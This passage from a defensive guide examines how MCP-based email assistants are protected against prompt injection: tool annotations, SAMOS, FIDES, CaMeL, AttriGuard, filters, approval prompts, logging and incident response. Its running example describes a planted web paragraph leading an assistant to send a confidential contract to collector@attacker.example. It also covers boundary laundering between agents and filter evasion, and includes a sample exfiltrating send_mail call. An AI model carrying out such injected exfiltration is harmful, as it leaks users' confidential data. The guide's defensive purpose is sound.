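The rule is easy to apply at the design stage, before anyone has written a policy. It is less helpful once it requires supervision, because it doesn't identify which calls a person should review. An agent with only two of the properties can also still do harm. For example, an agent without any private data could follow a planted instruction to order 400 printers.

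### What MCP's tool annotations can tell the host

To mark a session correctly, the host has to know which tools bring in outsiders' text. MCP has included tool annotations since March 2025, which let a server's author describe how a tool behaves. A search tool might have these:

```json
{
  "name": "web_search",
  "annotations": {
    "readOnlyHint": true,
    "openWorldHint": true
  }
}
```

A true `openWorldHint` means the tool deals with an open-ended set of outside entities rather than a closed domain. The host can treat it as a sign before the call that data may leave, and as a reason after the call to mark the session as tainted. If the hint is left out, it defaults to true. According to a March 2026 post by the Model Context Protocol maintainers, many servers come without annotations, and clients vary in how strictly they apply the cautious defaults.

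The hint is unreliable for mailboxes. A tool's author could reasonably set it to false for a tool that reads a single account, even if strangers wrote half the messages in it. The maintainers acknowledge that "external" may mean outside the company's network on one system and outside the user's computer on another. The hint also applies to the tool as a whole, so it does not distinguish a page from the company's own site from the carrier page. No current annotation marks a tool as reading private data.

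Annotations also don't enforce anything. A server can declare a tool read-only even if the tool deletes files, so the specification requires clients to distrust annotations from untrusted servers. Even an accurate annotation has no effect unless the host acts on it. The maintainers advise anyone who needs a guarantee that a tool can't leak data to use network controls or sandboxing.

A host that trusts its servers can still base useful rules on the hints. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, from June 2026, suggests always allowing read-only tools that work in a closed domain, but allowing those that reach the open world only if every argument is public. Under that rule, the manager's assistant could search freely until it opened the contract, but afterwards could not put the contract's price into a query. The send tool is not read-only, so it needs a separate rule.

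In March 2026 there were five open proposals for better labels, including a draft on trust and sensitivity annotations written jointly by GitHub and OpenAI. By July the Model Context Protocol's interest group on annotations counted six. The protocol's site still listed as an open question whether tool results should have annotations too. A search tool would need these to label one page differently from another.

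Microsoft has meanwhile put labels into MCP's general-purpose metadata field, and clients that don't recognise the labels can ignore them. GitHub's MCP server can now label content from public repositories as untrusted, and an experimental setting in GitHub's command-line assistant uses these labels. The setting doesn't yet cover all of that server's tools, or any other server. If a vendor advertises label support, the assessor should ask for a list of the tools it covers.

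### SAMOS: labels at a gateway

*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes SAMOS, a system that enforces labels without changing the model or the assistant. Whoever deploys the tools gives each one two confidentiality labels, one for what it reads and one for the places it writes to, and sets each label to high or low. All MCP calls pass through a gateway, which keeps a label for the session and compares it with the labels of each new tool.

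In the running example, the search tool reads public pages, so the session becomes low at step 4. The mail reader has a high label, so the gateway refuses the call to it at step 6. Denning's secrecy rule would have allowed this call, since reading a secret after a public page leaks nothing by itself. SAMOS is stricter because it in effect also treats public text as untrusted.

The manager therefore can't compare a web offer with the current contract in the same session. Ntousakis suggests that a confidential session could get public information through a different agent with its own session, though this brings back the problem of what the agents pass to each other.

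Two labels per tool are also too coarse for mail. The contract and a stranger's email both get the mail tool's high label, although only the contract deserves trust. Ntousakis discusses a similar problem with a tool that reads both public and private repositories. Either the tool must report a label with each result, or the developer must split it into two tools. A gateway also checks only the calls that pass through it, so it would miss an image in the reply or a call to a tool built into the host.

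The only evidence for SAMOS is a case study in which it blocks a known attack on GitHub's MCP server. Ntousakis gives no attack success or task-completion rates, so the design is plausible, but nobody has measured its drawbacks.

### FIDES: hiding the page from the planner

Costa and colleagues designed FIDES at Microsoft to avoid tainting the whole context. Each piece of data has a label with two parts: whether it is trusted, and who may read it. When the assistant combines two pieces of data, the result is untrusted if either piece was, and only people who could read both may read the result:

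$$R(x \text{ combined with } y) = R(x) \cap R(y)$$

Suppose only the manager and one supplier may read the contract, and only the manager and a rival supplier may read the rival's quote. Only the manager may then read a message based on both, so the assistant can't send it to either supplier. This rule also blocks accidental leaks. In a similar example from Microsoft, an assistant answering a backlog of email might, without such a rule, reveal sales figures to a curious colleague.

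FIDES checks two rules before a tool call:

- **Trusted action.** A consequential call may go ahead only if trusted data alone led to it.
- **Permitted flow.** Data may go only to recipients who are allowed to read it.

A host can require an email to satisfy both rules, or it can accept either one, as *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) does. If either rule is enough, the manager can deliberately share something confidential, but a planted instruction can't make the assistant share it.

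The main novelty is in how FIDES treats untrusted results. The planner is the model that decides what to do next, and FIDES hides the carrier page from it:

1. The planner calls the search tool. FIDES stores the untrusted result in a variable, and the planner sees only the variable's name.
2. The planner asks another model to write the comparison from that variable. This quarantined model has no tools.
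3. FIDES stores the comparison in another variable, and the planner passes it to the manager without reading it.

The planted paragraph reaches only a model that cannot call anything. It may spoil the comparison, but step 5 never happens.

Some tasks require the planner to know what a page contains. It can have the quarantined model return a yes or no, for example on whether a supplier delivers within a week. An attacker can falsify the answer but can't fit an instruction into a single yes or no. The planner can also open the variable and read everything, but this taints its context. It might then follow instructions in the page and read the contract, but the message to collector@attacker.example would break both rules at step 8.

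The table gives the share of AgentDojo tasks that GPT-4o completed when there was no attack:

| Set-up | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No control | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| One label for the whole context | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with its rules enforced | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

On average, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the simple tainted context, and 16 points more with o1, a stronger model at the time. It did worse on travel tasks, where many tools were allowed in a tainted context anyway and GPT-4o had trouble handling the variables. No attacks succeeded with the rules enforced. Hiding the page was not enough without them, since 21 attacks succeeded when the rules were switched off and the planner was free to open a variable and act on it.

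The guarantee has gaps that matter for email. Costa and colleagues treat the reply to the user as harmless in their basic design, so a chat window that loads outside images needs a separate rule. FIDES also doesn't prevent an observer from learning information from the assistant's choice of calls or their order. Ayush Paul's attack on Claude used this kind of leak to spell out a name through a choice of links.

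In May 2026 Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft warns in *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) that the framework treats unlabeled tools as trusted and public, the opposite of MCP's cautious default. If a developer forgets to label a web search tool, a page carrying an attacker's instructions enters as trusted text, with no visible sign of the mistake.

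### CaMeL: a plan fixed in advance

FIDES lets the planner choose each step as it goes, whereas CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, fixes the whole plan before any outside text arrives. In CaMeL, a privileged model turns the user's request into a short program, and a quarantined model without tools handles the text that tool calls return. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from, and checks a policy before each tool call.

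For the original request, the program would contain a search and a call to the quarantined model for the comparison, but no mail commands. The program already exists when the carrier page is read, so text on the page can't add a line to it, and the attack stops at step 5.

The harder case is a request that does involve mail. Suppose the manager asks the assistant to find the cheapest supplier's sales address and send that supplier the current contract, so that it can match the terms. The privileged model might write this program, simplified here:

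```python
page = web_search("label printer suppliers compared")
address = quarantined_model("Find the cheapest supplier's sales address", page)
contract = search_mail("label printer contract")
send_mail(to=address, body=contract)
```

This time the planted text only has to present the attacker's address as the supplier's. The interpreter records the following:

| Value | Content | Origin | Who may read it |
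|---|---|---|---|
| `page` | The search results, including the carrier page | The web | Anyone |
| `address` | collector@attacker.example | The web, through the quarantined model | Anyone |
| `contract` | The text of the contract email | The mailbox | The manager and the current supplier |

Using the quarantined model doesn't make the address any more trustworthy, because each value keeps a record of the origins of everything that went into it. When the program reaches the last line, the interpreter applies the policy by checking whether the recipient may read the body. The attacker is not among the contract's readers, and the address did not come from the manager, so the interpreter refuses the call at step 8.

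The plan alone would not have prevented this leak, because the program ran exactly as written and only one value was wrong. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this a data-flow attack and distinguishes it from an attack that changes which tools the agent calls. An assessor who hears that a product "uses CaMeL" should therefore ask to see the policy for sending mail.

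The interpreter would have refused the real supplier's address too, since it also came from the web and the supplier isn't one of the contract's readers. If the manager really does want to write to an address found online, there are several ways to do it:

- **Send only public information.** A request for a price list contains nothing confidential, so a policy that checks only who may read the body lets it through. A stricter policy that also requires a trusted recipient would not.
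- **Approve the call.** The host shows the manager the recipient and the content, and the manager decides.
- **Endorse the data.** The manager declares the address trustworthy, and the assistant can then use it without asking again.
- **Supply the address.** The manager checks the address against an old invoice, for example, and types it in. Copying it from the assistant's own comparison would give it a trusted label without making it any more reliable.

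Kolluri and colleagues built endorsement into Prudentia, an agent based on FIDES. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions. Prudentia also takes the policies into account when planning, so that it can work around them. On AgentDojo, it raised the share of tasks completed without human help by up to 9% over FIDES and reduced the number of interventions by a factor of up to 1.9. The manager would be safer endorsing only the address, because endorsing the whole page would also mark the planted paragraph as trusted.

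### What CaMeL costs, and where it leaks

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says CaMeL stops nearly all attacks in AgentDojo with comparable task performance. In a later test, reported in *AttriGuard* (2026), He, Zhu and colleagues ran CaMeL on Gemini 2.5 Flash. None of four standard attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 38% of ordinary tasks, down from 58% without a defence, and the average run took 165 seconds instead of 11.

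Most of the lost tasks require the agent to work out what to do along the way. A program written before the search results arrive can't add a step in response to them. The privileged model also has to know the format of every tool's output in advance, so somebody has to document those formats.

CaMeL reduced task success less for stronger models when Peters-Gill and colleagues tested it on industrial maintenance tasks shared between several agents. Across five models, the success rate fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points, but it fell by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5.

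They also found a way around CaMeL. In their experiment, which used three agents all protected by CaMeL, an orchestrating agent got job applicants' details from a database agent and passed a summary to a notification agent to send to a colleague on Slack. An instruction planted in the database ended up in the summary, which the notification agent received as part of its user's request. That agent's privileged model therefore read the instruction before writing the program, and added a line that emailed the data to an outside address.

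Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because untrusted text becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another. It automates what the manager does by pasting a whole comparison into the mail session. A product advertised as having separate search and mail agents has this weakness if one agent's output becomes part of the other's instructions. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives each agent one channel for instructions and another for data, and the interpreter keeps every tool's output out of the instructions.

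Five models each faced 949 attack cases on a version of AgentDojo divided among several agents. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and none with multi-CaMeL. The researchers switched off all policies for sending data, so these figures measure only the protection from a fixed plan. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, which suggests that the attacks were too weak to show much about the newest models.

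Even then, the web page can determine which branch runs if the program contains a choice, such as writing to one supplier if the price is below a limit and to another if it isn't. The interpreter that multi-CaMeL inherits can also miss this kind of dependence and leave a trusted label on a value that an untrusted condition has affected.

### AttriGuard: asking what caused the call

The Rule of Two restricts an assistant according to what it can do, whatever the reason for a particular call. AttriGuard, the system that He and colleagues built, instead tests whether the user's request or the outside text caused the call. When the model proposes a tool call, AttriGuard does the following:

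1. It rewrites the outside text to weaken its power to direct the model. It turns structured data that looks like a tool call into plain sentences, and commands into reports. An instruction to send a document becomes a statement that, according to the text, someone should send it.
2. It runs the model again with the same request and the same earlier actions, but with the rewritten text.
3. If the model proposes the same call again, AttriGuard lets the original call through. If the arguments differ, another model judges whether the call still serves the user's request.
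4. If the call has disappeared, AttriGuard blocks it and returns a warning instead of a result.

In the running example, the model proposes to look for the contract email at step 5. In the rerun, the page contains only a statement that AI assistants should find such an email, and a model asked to compare printers probably has no reason to look for one. AttriGuard then blocks the call at step 6. If the manager had asked for the contract, the model would propose the call in the rerun too, and AttriGuard would allow it. The Rule of Two would require supervision in both cases.

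AttriGuard stopped every attack that used fixed wording. With it, an agent running on Llama 3.3 70B completed 54% of ordinary tasks, compared with 60% without a defence. The average run on Gemini took 32 seconds, much less than with CaMeL.

Unlike CaMeL, AttriGuard offers no guarantee, because it relies on models to do the rewriting, the rerun and the judging. In a test by He and colleagues, an automated attacker could revise its text up to 200 times for each of 61 cases. The attacker succeeded in 4 cases on Gemini and 6 on Llama. Every successful attack aimed to get the agent to visit a certain website. The attacker only had to mention that more information was available there, which made the visit look like a sensible part of the task.

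This exception is a problem for an assistant that can open web pages, because a page request can carry data out. AttriGuard also doesn't try to protect a user who tells the agent to follow whatever a document says. For example, it wouldn't help if the manager asked the assistant to follow a supplier's ordering page that an attacker had altered.

### Input filters

A filter tries to detect planted instructions before they enter the context at step 4, as SearchInject does with search results. It is easy to add, but it relies on wording, which an attacker can change. In tests of several filters on Gemini 2.5 Flash by He and colleagues, an attack that posed as an important message from the user succeeded in 33.0% of cases without a filter and 19.8% with one called PromptGuard. Another filter, PIGuard, reduced the rate to 1.4%, but the agent then completed only 35% of ordinary tasks instead of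 58%. When the attacker could adapt, 52% of the attacks got past PIGuard.

Willison notes that vendors like to advertise that their filters catch 95% of attacks, which he considers a failing grade in web security. A filter is still worth having against crude attacks, as long as nobody relaxes another control because of it.

### Testing the controls without fooling the model

Controls in ordinary software are much easier to test than a model's resistance to attack, because the assessor can leave the model out. After a web result has entered the session, a script makes the calls that a fooled model would make, one to read a test message and one to send it to an outside address. If the host carries out both, the control isn't working. If it refuses, it should refuse every time, so the assessor can test each tool and outward channel instead of repeating the same attempt.

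To test the sending policy in FIDES and CaMeL, the script should also replace the quarantined model's answer with the attacker's address. AttriGuard and input filters depend on models, so they still need repeated trials with an attacker who adapts.

The table matches each control to the step of the running example at which it stops the attack:

| Control | Where the attack stops | Can a cleverly worded page get past it? |
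|---|---|---|
| Separate sessions | Step 6 | Only if someone or something carries its text across |
| Read-only mail | Step 8 | Yes, through another outward channel |
| Approved recipients | Step 8 | Yes, through another channel or to a wrong recipient on the list |
| Network limits | Nowhere, but they stop a leak through a page request | Yes, by mail or through an approved site that passes data on |
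| Tainted session | Step 6 or 8, depending on which tools the host blocks | Not if the host has marked every source and closed every channel |
| Rule of Two | Step 6 or 8, depending on which property the assistant gives up | Possibly, if a person approves the calls instead |
| MCP annotations alone | Nowhere | Yes |
| SAMOS | Step 6 | Not if the labels are right and the call passes through the gateway |
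| FIDES | Step 5, or step 8 if the planner opens the page | Not if the labels are right and the rules cover every channel |
| CaMeL | Step 5, or step 8 if the manager asked for mail to be sent | It can alter values and choose between planned branches |
| AttriGuard | Step 6, usually | Sometimes, if the planted goal looks like part of the task |
| Input filter | Step 4, sometimes | Yes |

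## What the user approves and what is recorded

Several of these controls end with an approval step. After the model writes a tool call, the host holds it and shows the user a prompt. If the user allows the call, the host passes it to the server. If the user refuses, the server never receives it, and the model gets a refusal as its tool result. In the running example, the host could ask before reading the contract email (between steps 5 and 6), before sending it (between steps 7 and 8), or both.

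The host's own code has to enforce the approval step. If the developer only tells the model to ask first, a planted instruction can override that. Microsoft (2026) describes how Copilot Studio, its tool for building agents, lets the builder mark a tool as needing approval regardless of the agent's instructions. A host can also use tool annotations to decide which calls to hold for approval. No approval step covers a leak that involves no tool call, such as one through an image address in the reply.

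### Two prompts for the same email

At step 8, the host could show the manager this:

```
The assistant wants to use the tool send_mail.

[Allow]   [Deny]
```

Or it could show this:

```
The assistant wants to send an email.

To:       collector@attacker.example
          You have never written to this address.
          It came from a web page: (address of the carrier page)
Content:  (full text of the contract email)

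[Send]   [Cancel]
```

With the first prompt, the manager can judge only whether the assistant should be sending anything at all. That is enough here, because the manager asked only for a comparison, which doesn't require sending anything. But if the manager had also asked the assistant to write to the cheapest supplier, the prompt would look the same whether the assistant was emailing a price enquiry to that supplier or the contract to a stranger.

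The second prompt shows that a confidential document is about to go to an unknown recipient. The line about the web page matters most when the attacker's address resembles a real supplier's. It doesn't prove an attack, since genuine sales addresses come from web pages too, but it gives the manager a reason to check the address.

The host should fill in these lines from the call's arguments and its own records. A description written by the model is unreliable, because a model that has followed the instructions on the carrier page may describe the message as a routine enquiry. The host can find where an address came from by searching the session's earlier tool results. This search fails if the model assembled the address from pieces, which is one reason to track origins as CaMeL does.

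Real approval prompts often fall between the two. In TechRadar's *I sent an email without opening Gmail thanks to ChatGPT's new feature*, the reporter saw a box that described the action and offered Allow and Deny, but had to click Details to read the exact email. Microsoft's *Get started with Cowork* describes a preview of the planned action and advises users to verify the recipients and content. It doesn't mention whether the preview shows where an address came from.

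### How people respond to repeated prompts

The best figures on user approval come from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant, which used to ask before running most commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of the prompts, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the figure at 97% by August 2026. Most of the commands were probably harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't show on its own that people had stopped reading the prompts. The same users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval, though people can reject a safe plan because they want something done differently.

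Anthropic also ran a more direct test. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Fatigue therefore lowered the refusal rate, but most testers approved the command even early in a session.

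The testers were not working on their own projects and had less to lose than a manager with a real contract. A shell command is also harder to judge than an email to a stranger. The refusal rate for a well-designed email prompt could be much higher, but the study did not measure it.

Many Claude Code users had also turned the prompts off. A quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips all permission checks.

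### Why Anthropic moved to automatic decisions

In March 2026 Anthropic introduced auto mode, in which a second model decides whether each risky action may go ahead. Anthropic first justified it as a convenience in *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026), because a user who has to approve every step can't start a large task and leave. In August Anthropic also argued that auto mode was safer than typical human review, and made it the default on most individual and team plans. In testing, the automatic check blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands (89%), including 800 that the testers had approved. The testers stopped only 6 that the check would have allowed.

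These rates can go into the yearly estimate from the section on measurement. With *n* exposures to a carrier page, a compliance rate *p* and a review that catches a share *c* of the bad calls, the chance of at least one leak is

$$1 - (1 - p(1 - c))^n$$

If an assistant encounters 60 malicious instructions and has a 2% chance of following each one, the chance of at least one leak is about 70% without review. Reviewers who catch 13.6% of bad tool calls lower it to 65%, and a check that catches 89% lowers it to 12%. These catch rates come from reviews of coding commands, so the results are only a rough indication for email.

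Two other tests are more relevant to planted instructions. Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, made 720 injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. However, only 0.09% succeeded on average against Anthropic's latest models with the checks switched off, so there was almost nothing left for auto mode to stop. The attacks had also been optimised against an older Claude model. In the other test, Apollo Research inserted synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. The check missed 12% of them at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it.

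As Anthropic first described it, the check receives the user's messages and the model's tool calls but not the tool results, so text on a web page can't influence it directly. This should work well in the original running example, because a request to compare printers plainly doesn't cover sending a contract to anyone. But if the manager has asked the assistant to send the contract to the cheapest supplier, the check can't determine whether the address belongs to the supplier or the attacker. Anthropic acknowledges that the check can't determine where such a value came from, and accepts this limitation in exchange for resistance to injection.

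Willison agrees that auto mode is better than constant questions but points out that the remaining 11% of dangerous actions would still have gone ahead. He wants more independent confirmation of the results on prompt injection.

### When a person should still decide

An approval prompt is the last chance to stop a message, and nobody can recall a contract once a stranger has it. In Embrace The Red's *Windsurf MCP Integration*, Rehberger showed that Windsurf, a coding assistant, carried out MCP calls without asking and had no setting to change this. A comment planted in source code led it to copy a message from a private Slack channel to a public one. Rehberger dislikes approval dialogs and expects people to click through them, but still considers them the best available protection for consequential actions such as sending email.

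Unattended tasks are a harder problem for approval prompts, because nobody is there to answer them. The host can wait, refuse or go ahead. ChatGPT can start a task when a new Gmail message arrives, and OpenAI says the task pauses if an action needs approval. Pausing is the safe choice for email, because a stranger can start such a task by writing to the user. Claude Code usually returns to manual prompts after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session, but if it is running without a user interface, it stops instead.

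For the manager's assistant, a reasonable compromise is for the host to refuse actions the manager would never want, send routine replies to known suppliers without asking, and prompt the manager only when a new recipient or a confidential document is involved. The manager would then see few prompts, each requiring a real decision. The Claude Code study suggests that this would help somewhat, but that the manager still couldn't be relied on to stop a leak.

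### How current assistants treat outgoing mail

The four large vendors have different rules. They appear in OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*, Anthropic's *Use Google Workspace connectors*, Google's *Use Gemini Spark to manage your tasks & workflows in Gemini Apps* and Microsoft's *Application card* for Copilot Cowork:

| Assistant | Before it sends an email | When the email may go out without a prompt |
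|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Depends on the permission level; OpenAI lists sending email among the actions that may need review | If the user has chosen "Allow all actions", which OpenAI offers only for some apps and accounts |
| Claude | Asks by default outside Auto mode | In Auto mode, unless the automatic check flags the email or the organisation requires approval |
| Gemini Spark | Google designed it to ask for confirmation | If this safeguard fails, which Google does not rule out |
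| Copilot Cowork | Pauses and shows a preview | After the user selects "Don't ask again", until the conversation ends |

When Claude became able to send Gmail messages in August 2026, it asked for approval first by default, 9to5Google reported. In late October, Anthropic began making Auto mode the default for new sessions in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans. A manager on one of these plans who has never changed the setting may therefore see no approval prompt. Anthropic warns that Auto mode's check "can miss risky actions". For browser work, Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* advises users to watch closely, or return to manual approval, when Claude sends messages in their name.

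Microsoft calls approval Cowork's primary safety mechanism, but the flaw Willison reported in May 2026 involved emails to the user's own inbox, which needed no approval. Google warns that a scheduled task may run while the user is offline and unable to stop it.

An assessor should check the setting on the account that people will use. According to Anthropic, owners of Claude's organisational plans can set each connector tool to "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked", and individual users can't override a restriction. If the send tool is blocked but the assistant can still read mail, a tired user never has to decide whether to approve sending an email.

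### Who is responsible when both servers worked correctly

Apify, a web-scraping company, offers an MCP server that lets an assistant read web pages and run data-collection jobs in the user's account. In 2026, Pluto Security reported that text on a page could make the assistant use this server to contact an address the attacker chose. The assistant did so in all eight trials with the same planted text.

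Apify closed the report, calling the problem "probably unsolvable" for autonomous agents. It placed the responsibility with users, who could run the agent in a restricted environment, approve every call or accept the risk. Pluto Security, which sells protection against such attacks, acknowledges the technical difficulty but objects that approving every call removes much of the reason people install the server. It proposes keeping web reading separate from tools that act on the user's account, recording where each argument came from, and asking the user when a page introduces a new destination.

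Apify is right that this differs from an ordinary bug. Pluto Security had also found that one of Apify's tools accepted any address beginning with the name of its documentation site, including docs.apify.com.evil.example. Apify could fix that flaw by changing the server's code, but it can't fix the assistant's decision to follow a page's instructions that way.

But that doesn't make the user solely responsible. In the running example, only the host handles both the web page and the mail call, so its maker is best placed to block the call or show a useful prompt. The company that connected the two servers and chose the approval settings is next best placed to prevent the leak. The manager is a poor final check, particularly if the prompt showed only a tool's name. This is a judgement about who could have prevented the leak; legal liability depends on contracts and local law.

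The question has become more pressing since the July 2026 revision of MCP. Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, argues that the revision shifts security enforcement from the protocol to endpoints and developers.

### Records that make a leak traceable

A list of tool names is not enough to reconstruct an attack. In Pluto Security's test, the assistant called Apify's page reader, fetched the stored text, and called the page reader again. The first and last calls used the same tool, and only their arguments showed that one went to the user's page and the other to the attacker's. For the running example, the record of step 8 should look something like this:

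```json
{
  "session": "4821",
  "tool": "send_mail",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "collector@attacker.example",
    "body": "(text of the contract email)"
  },
  "recipient_origin": "tool result 1, (address of the carrier page)",
  "approval": {
    "decision": "allowed",
    "decided_by": "automatic check",
    "text_shown_to_user": null
  },
  "result": "delivered"
}
```

The origin field links the email to the raw search result in the log. An investigator also needs the raw results from the mail server, because they show every message the model read, including any that leaked through another channel.

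The approval field should show whether the user approved the email individually, the user had earlier chosen "always allow", or the decision was automatic. If the user approved the email individually, the log should also keep the text of the prompt they saw, because their approval means little if the prompt read only "send_mail".

Products differ in what they record. OpenAI logs all app calls on its compliance platform for organisations. Cowork's side panel lists the tools and actions the user has approved, and Claude in Chrome has a permission history. A complete log contains private mail, so the company should restrict who can read it and decide how long to keep it.

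### Responding to the leak

Suppose the manager finds the message to collector@attacker.example in the sent folder. The response would go as follows:

1. **Stop the session and save the evidence.** The manager stops the assistant, pauses its scheduled tasks and exports the conversation. Deleting an alarming chat is a natural reaction, but with Claude it also deletes the mail data retrieved in that chat. Turning off Gemini Spark deletes the data from its remote browser.
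2. **Revoke access to the mailbox.** The manager disconnects the mail account in the assistant's settings, then removes the assistant's access in the mail provider's settings. Choosing a stricter permission level is not enough. OpenAI notes that changing an app's permission doesn't revoke access already granted.
3. **Remove forwarding rules.** Anthropic lists tools for creating and listing filters in its Gmail connector, but none for deleting them, so the manager has to delete any new rules in Gmail. An administrator should copy each suspicious rule before deleting it and find out which messages it affected.
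4. **Find out what was sent.** The investigator compares the logged calls with the mail system's own delivery records and checks page requests, links and images for private text. If the records are incomplete, the safest assumption is that everything the model read in the session may have leaked. The company changes any passwords in those messages and decides with its lawyers whom to inform, starting with the supplier named in the contract.
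5. **Search for other sessions that read the page.** The investigator searches the raw tool results of all the company's assistants for the page's address, for distinctive phrases from the planted paragraph and for the attacker's email address. Searching for the page's address alone would miss a copy on another site. Each match needs a check of the calls that followed it, as well as of anything the assistant saved to memory.
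6. **Change the host before reconnecting the mailbox.** Blocking the attacker's address stops only this version of the attack. The host should also refuse the same sequence of calls with a different page and recipient.

A company can use a dummy message to test whether its records would be enough to explain a real leak. One person has the assistant read a harmless test page and send the message to an address the company controls. A colleague who didn't watch then uses only the records to try to identify the page, the message, the recipient, and who or what approved sending it.
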